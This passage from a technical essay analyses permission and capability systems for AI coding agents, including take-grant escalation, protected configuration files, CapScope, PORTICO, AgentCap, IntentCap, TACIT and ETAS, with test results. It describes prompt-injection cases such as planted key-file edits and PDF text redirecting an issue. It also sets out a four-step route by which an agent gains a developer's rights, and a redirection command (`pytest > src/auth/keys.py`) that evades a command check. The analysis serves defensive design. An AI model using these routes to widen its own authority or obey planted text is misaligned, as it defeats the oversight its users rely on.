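### How the take-grant model avoids the problem

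The take-grant model makes the question decidable by fixing the commands in advance. It represents a system as a graph in which an arrow from one subject or object to another carries the rights the first has over the second. Two special rights control sharing:

- If A has the *take* right over B, A can copy any right that B has.
- If A has the *grant* right over B, A can give B any right that A has.

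The only other commands let a subject create something new, with any rights over it, or give up rights it already has. *Foundational Results*, a textbook chapter on these models, credits Jones, Lipton and Snyder with a 1976 system in which the time needed to decide security grows in proportion to the system's size. *A linear time algorithm for deciding subject security* (Lipton and Snyder, 1977) also gives such an algorithm.

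Deciding whether a subject could gain a right becomes easier because rights to existing objects spread only by copying along take and grant arrows. If every node in the graph is a subject that can act, the algorithm only has to check whether a chain of these arrows connects the subject that has the right to the one that might get it. Creating new subjects doesn't change the answer, however large the graph grows, because a new subject is at first connected only to its creator and so can't join two separate parts of the graph.

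The direction of the arrows doesn't matter if both sides cooperate. Suppose a developer has the take right over her agent, so she can use anything it has, but the agent has no rights over her. It may seem that permissions can flow only towards the developer. Yet the agent could obtain her right to read the organization's repositories in four steps:

1. The agent creates a folder and receives take and grant rights over it.
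2. The developer uses her take right over the agent to copy its grant right over the folder.
3. She grants the folder her right to read the repositories.
4. The agent takes that right from the folder.

A user might save an access token in a folder the agent had made. The model assumes this could happen, which is reasonable given how readily users approve requests.

The simple rules leave out much of what a real policy needs. A subject with the grant right can pass on any right it has, and the model provides no way to require a second person's approval or restrict which rights a subject may share.

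For most agents, the easiest solution is to provide no commands that add access rights. The agent's permissions then stay fixed, and nobody has to analyse long sequences of edits. If a person can approve new rights during a session, the analysis also depends on that person. Harrison and colleagues would leave a subject out of the access matrix only if it were reliable. A human approver may not meet that standard, since most of Anthropic's testers failed to stop the dangerous command they saw.

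### Protecting configuration files

A harness can apply this by preventing the agent from editing the files that define its permissions. Codex keeps `.git` and `.codex` read-only inside an otherwise writable project. Bolin explains that this prevents direct changes to Git hooks and to `.codex/config.toml`, which contains Codex's settings. An organization's restrictions on its users are in a separate file, `requirements.toml`, as OpenAI's own configuration shows. Because Git stores new commits in `.git`, protecting that directory also means that a sandboxed agent can't commit its work without an exception.

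A list of protected folders can't cover every file that might later run outside the sandbox. Bolin gives the example of Prettier, a code formatter that a project may keep in its `node_modules` folder of installed packages. If an agent altered that copy and the developer's editor ran Prettier on every save, the altered code would run outside the sandbox. Git often ignores `node_modules`, so `git status` might not show the change. OpenAI relies on the model's training to reduce the risk of actions that the sandbox permits.

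NVIDIA recommends putting the whole code editor in the sandbox, along with everything it starts. Prettier would then run under the same limits as the agent. This is safer than trying to list every file that an editor might execute, but some developers' other tools will stop working.

Claude Code doesn't automatically approve writes to protected paths in most modes. Anthropic lists `.git`, `.claude`, `.vscode`, `.idea` and `.husky` as protected folders, which mostly contain settings for Git, Claude Code and code editors. The mode that bypasses permissions skips the prompts for these writes too, so a user who chooses it for convenience loses the protection for the agent's configuration.

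These paths matter because several programs run outside Claude Code's sandbox, including the user's hook commands and local MCP servers. Anthropic says the sandbox also doesn't cover the built-in tools for reading and editing files, which follow the permission rules instead. An administrator who wants to protect a file therefore needs both a sandbox restriction and a permission rule, because a permission rule for the file editor may not stop a script.

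NVIDIA's red team, which tests systems by attacking them, recommends the strictest approach, which is to block every write by the agent to configuration files, wherever they are. The user could not approve an exception in the editor and would have to make the change by hand. The block would cover instruction files such as `CLAUDE.md` as well as hooks, skills and the settings for local MCP servers. Researchers have found vulnerabilities that let untrusted content alter an agent's configuration. NVIDIA's *Mitigating Indirect AGENTS.md Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* describes one that OpenAI judged to add little to the existing risk of a compromised dependency.

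Under NVIDIA's rule, the gate would refuse the dependency update's edit to `AGENTS.md`. The agent could still suggest the new line in its final message, and the developer could paste it in. Pasting it in takes more effort than clicking "approve", which may make her think about the change. The rule suits hooks and permission files, which most projects seldom change. It is harder to justify for instruction files, because many teams want agents to help keep them up to date.

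GitLab lets an agent propose a configuration change without putting it into effect. It reads the agent configuration file only from a project's default branch, which is normally the main version of the code. An agent can edit the file on another branch, but the new settings apply only after someone merges that branch. So the agent can't loosen its own limits during a task, and the change appears in an ordinary code review.

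The merge still needs a careful reviewer, because the file can contain a setup script that runs before the sandbox starts. The script can read every environment variable, including an access token for the user who started the task. GitLab recommends that projects require a security reviewer to approve changes to the file. This protection also fails if the agent has permission to merge its own branches.

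### Agents designed to change

Some agents are supposed to modify themselves. Zhang (2026), in *Agent libOS*, presents a harness for agents that can save memories, load skills, write new tools, create child agents and restore earlier versions of themselves. Its main rule is that an agent may change what it can ask for, but doing so can't expand what it is authorized to affect. If *A* is the set of actions the model can see and request, *C* is its authority over existing resources, and Δ⁺ means an expansion, then

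Δ⁺*A* ⇏ Δ⁺*C*.

Suppose the agent in the dependency update writes a tool called `publish` and adds it to its list of tools, so that *A* now includes a new action. When the agent calls `publish`, the harness checks the push to the shared repository just as it would check a push from the command line. If the agent has no authority over that repository, the call fails, whatever the tool's name or description.

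Before a call can affect anything, it must meet several conditions at once:

admit = running ∧ authorized ∧ within the task's ceiling ∧ approved ∧ within budget ∧ through a known operation.

"Authorized" means the agent has a record, which Zhang calls a Capability, that covers this operation on this resource. The ceiling is a separate limit that the host can set for a task, so an agent with broad authority may be able to use only part of it. Approval can come from a fixed policy or a person, but it can't replace missing authority. Because approval is only one of the conditions in Agent libOS, one careless click isn't enough to let a call through, unlike in most coding agents.

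The same principle applies when an agent copies or restores itself. A parent agent can give its child no more authority than it has. An agent restored from an old checkpoint gets back only the authority that its source still has, so it can't recover a permission that someone has since withdrawn. An agent does receive rights over new objects it creates, much as a user owns a file she has made.

An agent can enter rights for its children in the access matrix, but the agent and its descendants together can't gain authority over an existing resource unless the host grants it. This makes the worst case much easier to determine, because an administrator can check what the first agent received instead of analysing every tool it might later write.

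In Zhang's tests of the full system, all 33 tasks succeeded and passed the safety checks. Agent libOS allowed none of 119 unauthorized effects and made no false denials, also out of 119. In another test with a real model, 13 of 15 runs were fully correct whether the model got its tools through skills or saw all of them at once. These results are evidence that the program follows its design on the cases Zhang chose. They give little indication of how often it would fail against a determined attacker, and Zhang doesn't present them as general rates.

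The design also depends on every effect passing through its checks. Zhang notes that a local MCP server runs as ordinary code under the host's account, so the administrator has to trust that program. Agent libOS doesn't stop planted text from changing an agent's plan. An agent authorized to email customers could learn from a malicious document to send misleading messages, and keep sending them without exceeding its permissions.

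### Memory and skills

Despite that risk, there are good reasons to let agents remember things. Jin and colleagues point to Reflexion, which stores written feedback on its attempts and uses it to make better decisions later, without changing the model's weights. Another system, Voyager, plays the video game *Minecraft* and saves working programs in a library of reusable skills. A coding agent's note that the tests need a particular time zone could save the developer from explaining it every week.

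Requiring approval for every note would remove much of this benefit and add to the prompts that users already ignore. But a false or malicious note can affect later sessions in which nobody sees the page it came from. Jin and colleagues also warn that memory can expose sensitive information in later tasks, and that a new skill can allow actions the user didn't expect.

A reasonable compromise is to let the agent save short notes without approval, but record the source of each note and keep the notes out of the reviewing model's input. The user should be able to read and delete them. The harness should treat them as information about how to do a task, never as evidence of permission. If the agent has saved a note that the developer always allows pushes, the gate should still require her approval for the next push.

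Skills that contain code need more care. The harness can let an agent write and use one within the current sandbox, because the skill has no more access there than any other program. The harness should require review before the skill runs outside the sandbox or becomes available to other users. Changes to shared instructions can wait until the end of a task, when the developer can review them together. She may pay more attention then, since Claude Code users reject plans far more often than individual permission requests.

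In the dependency update, the agent would finish its work under the old `AGENTS.md` and show the developer its proposed line along with the code changes. She could accept, edit or drop the line before the next session loads the file. The request for a broader token would not go to her for review, because the agent doesn't need access to the other repositories to update a date library.

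## How effect labels compare with capability-based security

A token that covers all of an organization's repositories gives its holder permission in every one of them, even if the task concerns only one. Capability-based security instead gives a program a reference to one particular object, and the reference itself grants permission to use that object.

Norm Hardy explained the problem that capability-based security solves in *The Confused Deputy* (1988), using an accident with a compiler. A company that sold computer time kept the compiler in a directory called SYSX and let it write to any file there, so that it could record usage statistics. The directory also held the company's billing records. Users could name a file to receive debugging output, and one user named the billing file. Because the compiler had permission to write in SYSX, the operating system opened the file, and the debugging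 output replaced the billing records.

The compiler is the confused deputy. It used the company's permission to write statistics. It should have used the user's permission to write her debugging output, but a file name doesn't record whose permission applies. An effect label wouldn't have helped much, because both acts write to a file in SYSX, which the company allowed. A rule protecting the billing file would have prevented this accident if someone had thought of it beforehand.

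With capabilities, the user opens the output file herself and passes the compiler a reference to it. She can't open the billing file, so she can't pass a reference to that file. The compiler uses its own reference for the statistics.

A coding agent is in much the same position as the compiler. Bouras and colleagues describe prompt injection as a confused-deputy problem, since the harness has the user's privileges while the model chooses the names of the files to use them on. The model may have taken a file name from the user's request or from a stranger's comment, and the name looks the same either way.

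### What a capability is

Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn introduced the term "capability" in *Programming Semantics for Multiprogrammed Computations* (1966). In their design, the operating system keeps a list of capabilities for each running computation. Each capability points to an object, such as a segment of memory, and records what the computation may do with it. A program uses a capability by giving its position in the list. It can't write new entries itself, so it can't refer to an object that nobody has given it.

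Such a list resembles one row of an access matrix, which shows who may use what. In *Capability Myths Demolished* (2003), Mark Miller, Ka-Ping Yee and Jonathan Shapiro dispute the common view that capabilities are just another way to store the same permissions. The matrix leaves out how a program identifies the object it wants to use. If the program gives a name and the system then looks up the program's permissions, the program can become a confused deputy. A capability combines these steps by both identifying the object and granting permission to use it.

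Miller's doctoral thesis, *Robust Composition* (2006), develops capability-based security for programming languages, where a reference to a software object is the permission to call it. A program has a reference only if it started with one, created the object, or received the reference from another program that had it. Miller also distinguishes permission from authority, which includes whatever a program can cause through other programs. An agent without permission to write to a file may still have authority over it if another agent will edit it on request.

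An effect label describes the kind of action a call performs, while a capability gives its holder permission to act on a particular object. An edit to `package.json` is labeled write(`package.json`) whichever agent proposes it, but only an agent that holds a capability for that file can make the edit.

Linux uses the word for something else. Its capabilities divide the powers of the administrator's account into classes, such as `CAP_CHOWN`, which lets a process change the owner of any file. They don't refer to a particular object, so they are closer to OpenBSD's `pledge` groups than to anything in Dennis and Van Horn. (CaMeL uses "capabilities" for the tags it puts on data, which is different again.)

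### One file, handed over and taken back

Suppose the agent updating the date library can read and write `package.json`, and wants a sub-agent to list the outdated packages. The sub-agent only has to read the file, and only for a minute or so. In a language with capabilities, the agent's program might look like this:

```
manifest = open_file("package.json")       # can read and write
reader = read_only(manifest)               # can only read
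link, cut_off = make_revocable(reader)     # works until cut off
start_subagent("List outdated packages", link)
# the sub-agent reports back
cut_off()
```

The second line narrows the permission by creating `reader`, an object that offers only the reading half of `manifest`. The sub-agent can't use `reader` to recover the other half. The third line creates a forwarder, `link`, which relays each request to `reader`. Passing `link` to the sub-agent delegates the permission, and no administrator has to add the sub-agent to a policy first. The last line revokes the sub-agent's access by making `link` stop relaying requests. Miller, Yee and Shapiro use such forwarders to answer the common belief that capabilities can't be revoked.

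If the sub-agent had shared `link` with a helper, the helper would lose access at the same moment. But the agent must create the forwarder before delegating, because it could not revoke access if it had passed `reader` directly. Revocation blocks only future requests, so the sub-agent keeps whatever it has already read.

### The comparison

| Matter | Effect labels | Capabilities |
|---|---|---|
| Ambient authority | remains in place; the gate restricts how the agent uses it | disappears, if the program has no other way to reach objects |
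| Delegation to sub-agents | needs a separate policy for each agent | the holder passes on a reference and can narrow it first |
| Revocation | someone changes the rule for every call it covers | someone cuts off one reference, if they prepared for it |
| Audit | the log shows what kind of act each call was | the log can show which grant permitted each call |
| Stating a policy | one rule can cover objects that nobody has listed | someone has to hand over each file, folder or account |
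| Irreversible acts within granted authority | the gate can refer them for review | the holder can simply perform them |

The case for capabilities is strongest when agents delegate work to sub-agents. A gate that applies one policy to a whole session gives every sub-agent the permissions that any of them needs. Separate policies for each agent help only if the harness preserves each agent's limits during delegation. *ETAS* (Tan, Wang and colleagues, 2026) collects reports of failures to do this. In Goose, a coding agent, a user's session required approval for sensitive tools, but a sub-agent started in automatic mode and ran them without asking. A Codex sub-agent assigned a read-only review generated an unrelated image and saved it outside the repository. With capabilities, a sub-agent can act only through the references it receives, so a missing setting leaves it with too little access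 instead of too much.

Effect labels are most useful when the agent already has permission to act. A developer could give her agent a capability to write to the shared repository so it can push a branch. The same capability might also let it overwrite the branch's history. A capability check allows both actions because the agent holds a valid capability for the repository. A gate that labels the overwrite as an irreversible write can stop it and ask for approval.

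Capability-based security can handle this case if the developer hands over a narrower reference, one that can add branches but can't rewrite them. A careful designer would build the tool this way, but would first have to decide which operations are irreversible and separate them from the rest. That is a classification by effect, which the capability then enforces.

The two approaches also suit different kinds of policy. "Ask before sending anything outside the company" is easy to state as an effect rule and covers destinations that don't exist yet, while a capability policy would have to list the permitted destinations. But capabilities can grant some permissions without a written policy. When a user selects two PDF files for an agent to work on, the selection itself can give the agent access to only those files.

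An investigator doing an audit usually wants records of both which calls deleted something and who had authorized them. Capabilities can make the link between a call and its authorization hard to break. In AgentCap, a system that issues signed tokens to agents, the code that approves a request also writes the log entry and puts the entry's identifier into the token before signing it. A plain reference that agents pass around freely leaves no such trail unless a forwarder logs its use.

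Effect labels fit existing software better than capabilities do. Shells, package managers and test runners refer to files by name and use the permissions of the account they run under. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* points out that a traditional capability system has to pass each capability from the program's entry point to every function that needs it, which usually means restructuring the whole program. Few teams would restructure a tool like `npm` this way, so most capability systems for agents leave the tools as they are and check permissions in the harness.

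### CapScope: an effect with a scope

In CapScope, the gate that Bouras and colleagues built, each permission is a capability Cap[*e*, φ], where *e* is an effect type (read, write or execute) and φ is a true-or-false test on the arguments. The capability covers a proposed call (*t*, *a*) if tool *t* has effect *e* and φ(*a*) is true. For a file, φ checks that the path lies under a given folder after resolving symbolic links and dot segments. For a command, φ checks that every part begins with an approved program and arguments.

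Three rules govern these capabilities.

- **Mint** creates them. Before the agent reads any file, a model sees the user's request and the names of the project's files, and predicts what the task will need. Ordinary code checks the prediction and freezes it as the ceiling for the session.
- **Derive** narrows them for a sub-agent. The delegating agent proposes some permissions, and the harness keeps those that lie within the ceiling. Cap[*e*, φ′] lies within Cap[*e*, φ] if φ′(*a*) implies φ(*a*) for all arguments *a*, so `src/**` can become `src/parser.py` but not the reverse.
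- **Invoke** checks each call. The call runs only if the agent proposing it has a capability that covers it.

This amounts to the subset rule with a separate set of allowed effects for each agent. In the doctored test example, the attacker plants a message requesting a new signing key in `src/auth/keys.py`. A single policy for the task must permit writes to `src` so that the bug can be fixed, which also permits the attacker's edit. CapScope gives the write permission to a patching agent. The agent that runs the tests and reads the planted message can read test files and run `pytest`, but has no write capability.

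The test in which a list of forbidden commands barely helped also covered two stricter policies, one of them CapScope. Each of the four policies had 75 runs, three for every combination of five repair tasks and five hiding places for the planted instruction, for a total of 300. The same four agents shared the work in every run.

| Policy | Planted action took effect | Repairs completed | Mean time |
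|---|---|---|---|
| No restrictions | 47 of 75 | 72 of 75 | 145 s |
| List of familiar hazards | 46 of 75 | 70 of 75 | 140 s |
| One policy written for the task | 33 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 194 s |
| CapScope | 3 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 316 s |

The drop from 33 to 3 is the most interesting because a model that had seen only trusted input generated both policies. Most of the attacks that still succeeded under the task policy used actions that some agent legitimately needed to take. All three attacks that got past CapScope came through `AGENTS.md`. Planted text can influence how the coordinating agent words a subtask, and therefore which permissions it requests for the sub-agent. The harness grants any request within the ceiling.

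Runs with CapScope took on average more than twice as long as runs without restrictions, partly because agents kept retrying refused calls. Five runs reached the 15-minute limit. Seven repairs failed. Two of them failed because the model predicting what the task would need had left out the write permission. In two others, the agent running the tests worked out the fix, but the patching agent never received it. The remaining three ran out of time with the tests already passing.

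Bouras and colleagues call CapScope "a host-side reference monitor rather than an object-capability system". The model refers to files by name, and the harness looks up each name in a table. An agent can therefore still be a confused deputy within its permissions. For example, if the patching agent is allowed to write anywhere in `src`, a planted comment can direct it to the wrong file there.

The check on commands has a larger gap, because CapScope removes redirections before it compares a command with the approved list and leaves their effects to a sandbox. This means `pytest > src/auth/keys.py` counts as running the tests, though it overwrites the key file. Only the sandbox can stop an agent without a write capability from doing this. Search commands such as `grep` can also read files outside the folders the agent is allowed to read.

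### Permissions that end with the subtask

CapScope's permissions last for the session of the agent that has them. Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Lingering Authority*, presents PORTICO, which withdraws a permission when the subtask that required it ends. In the paper's example, an agent has to carry a timeout setting from one file to another:

1. At the start, the agent can use `src/api.py`, its test file and the test command.
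2. It tries to read `notes/packaging.md`. The task's contract forbids this, so PORTICO refuses.
3. It asks for `src/serialization.py`. The contract allows this file on request, and PORTICO issues one handle for reading it and another for writing.
4. The agent reads and edits the file through the handles.
5. The tests pass. PORTICO cancels the handles and removes them from the options the agent sees.
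6. The agent tries an old handle again, and PORTICO refuses.

A handle is a short code, such as `g0001:r1`, that has meaning only within PORTICO. It works rather like a position in Dennis and Van Horn's list, since the agent can quote it but can't make a valid one. PORTICO ends a permission when a test that it launched itself passes, or when a person or the surrounding workflow ends the subtask. The model can't close or extend a permission by stating that it has finished.

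To isolate the value of revocation, Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with a version that issued the same permissions at the same moments but never withdrew them. Both versions completed all ten runs of a test task. When the agent later tried to reread a file from the finished subtask, PORTICO refused every time and the comparator allowed it every time. In six further cases, a script tried to write through an expired handle. PORTICO blocked all six writes, and the comparator allowed them. Six cases with a live model, covering file writes, changes to Git and network requests, had the same results.

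These numbers are small, and the result follows almost directly from the design, since a system without revocation can't refuse a request because access was revoked. Santos-Grueiro describes the scripted test as a check that the program follows its protocol. The live model received a planted instruction to reuse the expired handle, so the tests don't measure how often an agent would misuse leftover access in ordinary work.

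In PORTICO's tests, agents completed fewer tasks when their permissions could be revoked. On 37 coding tasks, each run five times, PORTICO completed 161 of 185 runs, while a fixed list of permissions completed 180. In a supplementary test on real Python projects, PORTICO completed 31 of 42 runs, and a version without revocation completed all 42. Some contracts ended a permission too early or offered no way to renew it, and some models never requested it again. A harness that lets the user renew a permission with one click would prevent some of these failures, but it would add another prompt.

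### Permissions that end with the call

A permission can also expire after a set time or number of uses. *AGENTCAP* (Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, 2026) issues a signed token for each approved tool call. In its banking example, the token for a payment lasts 30 seconds and works once. The agent must have checked the balance first, and the recipient can't come solely from untrusted text.

An agent can delegate its token to a child agent in the same session. If *a* is the token's action, *r* its resource, *b* its remaining number of uses, *e* its expiry time and *d* the number of further delegations allowed, the child's token must satisfy

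*a*′ = *a*, *r*′ = *r*, *b*′ ≤ *b*, *e*′ ≤ *e*, *d*′ < *d*.

The last condition guarantees that every chain of delegation ends. The first two mean that delegation can shorten a permission but can't narrow what it covers. A parent with a token for a folder can't use it to give its child access to just one file, and would need a separate token for that file. CapScope's Derive rule does allow this narrowing.

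| Benchmark and model | Attacks that succeeded without AgentCap | With AgentCap | Fall in tasks completed without attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.63% | 5.09% | 3.1 points |
| AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.23% | 0.00% | 7.2 points |
| InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.24% | 8.63% | 11.7 points |
| InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 11.95% | 0.00% | 5.9 points |

Each figure comes from a single run over the whole benchmark. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao wrote the AgentDojo policies from the tools and the descriptions of the user tasks, then froze them before testing. A company writing a policy for its staff wouldn't have a complete list of their future requests, so it should expect either more refusals or looser rules. The short lifetime probably has little effect on these results, because an agent that obeys a planted instruction tends to do so at once. The check on where the recipient came from addresses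 the attack more directly.

AgentCap also keeps a trust score for each agent, which falls by 30% after every refused or suspicious call. With the default settings, the agent loses its write permissions after two such calls and all its permissions after three. This contains an agent that keeps probing for gaps. It may also give an attacker an easy way to disrupt work, since planted text that provokes three refusals would shut down an agent that had done no harm.

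*LLM Agent Capabilities Should Follow Task Intent and Context Source* (Zheng, Zhang and Mao, 2026) applies the confused-deputy argument to the individual fields of a call. In its example, a user asks an agent to extract tables from two PDFs and open one issue in a named GitHub repository. Hidden text in a PDF tells the agent to open the issue in the attacker's repository instead. Like the invoice in PROVISO's example, the PDF is allowed to supply data but not the destination.

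The IntentCap system therefore lets each kind of source fill only certain fields of a short-lived permission, called a lease. The user supplies the goal, the destination and any approvals. A skill supplies the procedure, the tool's definition supplies the form of the call, and files and tool results supply data. A model drafts the lease from these sources, and a fixed program checks that each field came from the right one. In the example, the lease permits one issue in the user's repository and expires when the agent uses it. The check also catches honest mistakes, such as the agent misreading a table heading as the repository's name.

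IntentCap accepted none of 3,746 unsafe events replayed from four benchmarks. When Zheng and colleagues merged the four sources into one trusted category, the checker wrongly accepted 3,593 of 3,823 events, or 94%. This is good evidence that the checker depends on keeping the sources separate. But they tested it on recorded events, not by attacking a working agent, and they didn't test attacks on the step that labels the sources, which they left for future work. Labeling is hard in ordinary use because a user may paste a stranger's document into a request. When the source is unclear, IntentCap doesn't let the content influence destinations or approvals.

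### What held capabilities imply about effects

Capabilities can also supply effect labels. Craig, Potanin and colleagues showed how in *Capabilities: Effects for Free* (2018). If a piece of code can reach the outside world only through the capabilities it receives, its effects can't exceed theirs. For code that holds capabilities *c*₁ to *c*ₙ and has effect ε,

ε ⊆ eff(*c*₁) ∪ … ∪ eff(*c*ₙ),

where eff(*c*) is everything that someone could do by using *c*. This includes indirect effects. If one of the capabilities is a function that writes to a log, the bound includes that write.

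Capabilities bound a script's effect without anyone analysing or annotating the code. Suppose an agent writes a script and the harness gives it only two capabilities, one to read `package.json` and one to add lines to `build.log`. The script's effect is at most read(`package.json`) ∪ write(`build.log`), even if it is a thousand lines long and builds more code as it runs. Static analysis has to assign ⊤ (any possible effect) to code like that.

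If the effect of every capability the script holds is within the allowed set *A*, the effect of anything the script does is also within *A*. The gate can therefore check the capabilities once, when it grants them, instead of labeling each later call. This check can overestimate the script's effects, since a script that is allowed to write to a file might never do so. It also fails if the language gives the script any other way to access outside resources, as ordinary Python does with its built-in `open` function.

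### Tracked capabilities in Scala

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* applies this relation in TACIT, a tool that runs Scala 3 programs written by an agent. The compiler records in each value's type which capabilities the value can use. For example, `String ->{f} Unit` is the type of a function that takes text, returns nothing and may use file `f`. If the set in braces is empty, the function is pure, like an expression with Lucassen's empty effect. The compiler checks these types before the program runs and rejects code that uses a capability its type doesn't mention.

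This gives a second way to end a permission. An agent that wants to use files asks for them in a block of code, and the capability is valid only inside the block. It might try to keep the access for later:

```
val later = requestFileSystem("project"): files =>
  () => files.access("package.json").read()
later()
```

The block returns a function that would read `package.json` after the block ends. The function's type must include `files`, but `files` doesn't exist outside the block, so the compiler rejects the program. PORTICO rejects an expired handle when the agent tries to use it, whereas here the program never runs. TACIT still checks at run time that the path is inside the requested folder.

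TACIT protects secrets with the same types. Reading a secret file returns its contents in a wrapper called `Classified`, and code can process the contents only with pure functions. Such a function could count the words in a contract but couldn't send the text anywhere, because it has no capability for sending data. If the agent prints the result, the user sees it, but the agent's model receives only a row of asterisks. The agent can have a separate, trusted model summarize the document, and the summary stays in the wrapper too.

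The main safety test combined each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 planted attacks and added 11 malicious requests, for 131 trials with each model. Without the wrapper, secrets appeared in the agent's output in 2 trials with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and 11 with MiniMax M2.5. With the wrapper, no secrets appeared. Claude resisted all 120 planted attacks without the wrapper, so the evidence that types improve on a well-trained model comes from two malicious requests. The stronger argument for types is that their protection doesn't depend on which model writes the code.

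Writing Scala didn't seem to make the agents less useful. On simulated customer service tasks, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with Scala than with ordinary tool calls. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of real programming problems, MiniMax solved 41.7% with Scala and 43.3% without it. Results against CaMeL on AgentDojo were more mixed. With OpenAI's o4-mini, TACIT completed 52.9% of workspace tasks and CaMeL 81.4%, but with Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT completed 64.3% of travel tasks and CaMeL 1.4%.

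The guarantee covers only Scala code. If the agent's program starts `npm test`, the compiler can't check what the tests do, and the user needs a sandbox again. Even within Scala, a program that may write to `package.json` may also empty it, because the types record which capability the code uses but don't distinguish more harmful writes from less harmful ones.

### ETAS: effects, order and grants

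ETAS, a programming language that Tan and colleagues designed for agents, combines effect labels with separate grants. Each function declares which effects may leave it, and the compiler rejects the function if any others could. When the program runs, it can take an outside action only if the declaration includes that kind of effect and the host has granted that operation with those arguments. The grant partly serves as a capability, but the host keeps it and the program never receives a reference.

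ETAS can also require effects to happen in a certain order. A rule such as

`Approval.request >> Repo.apply`

means that a program must request approval before it asks to change the repository. The compiler checks the possible sequences in advance. Where it can't settle the matter, it leaves a monitor in the program that blocks a forbidden request as it occurs.

Approval rules usually fail when a program has a preview mode, because a previewed write changes nothing and so isn't reported as an effect. ETAS records every request, including those a preview intercepts. A reviewing agent that must never write therefore fails the check if it contains a previewed write, so the problem is found before anyone turns the preview off.

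The ordering rule requires only that the program request approval before a write, so even a denied request satisfies it. The program's own `if` statement has to check whether approval was granted, and the host has to check consent before it carries out the write. One request also satisfies the rule for every later write, which makes it a standing approval unless the host's grants are narrower.

The evidence for these checks is thin so far. Tan and colleagues ran a coding agent's file-reading component through 10 scripted scenarios. Four finished normally and six stopped where they should have. The compiler accepted two small, valid test programs and rejected four small ones with deliberate faults, such as a missing approval. Tan and colleagues also prove the main properties for a simplified version of the language, assuming that every effect goes through the host.

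In a further experiment, the researchers let an agent for financial questions revise its own prompts and processing code over five generations. Each revision had to compile against a fixed set of declared types, effect limits and ordering rules before it could run, so the agent could change how it worked but could not give itself a new kind of effect. Accuracy on 256 questions rose from 69.9% to 78.9%.
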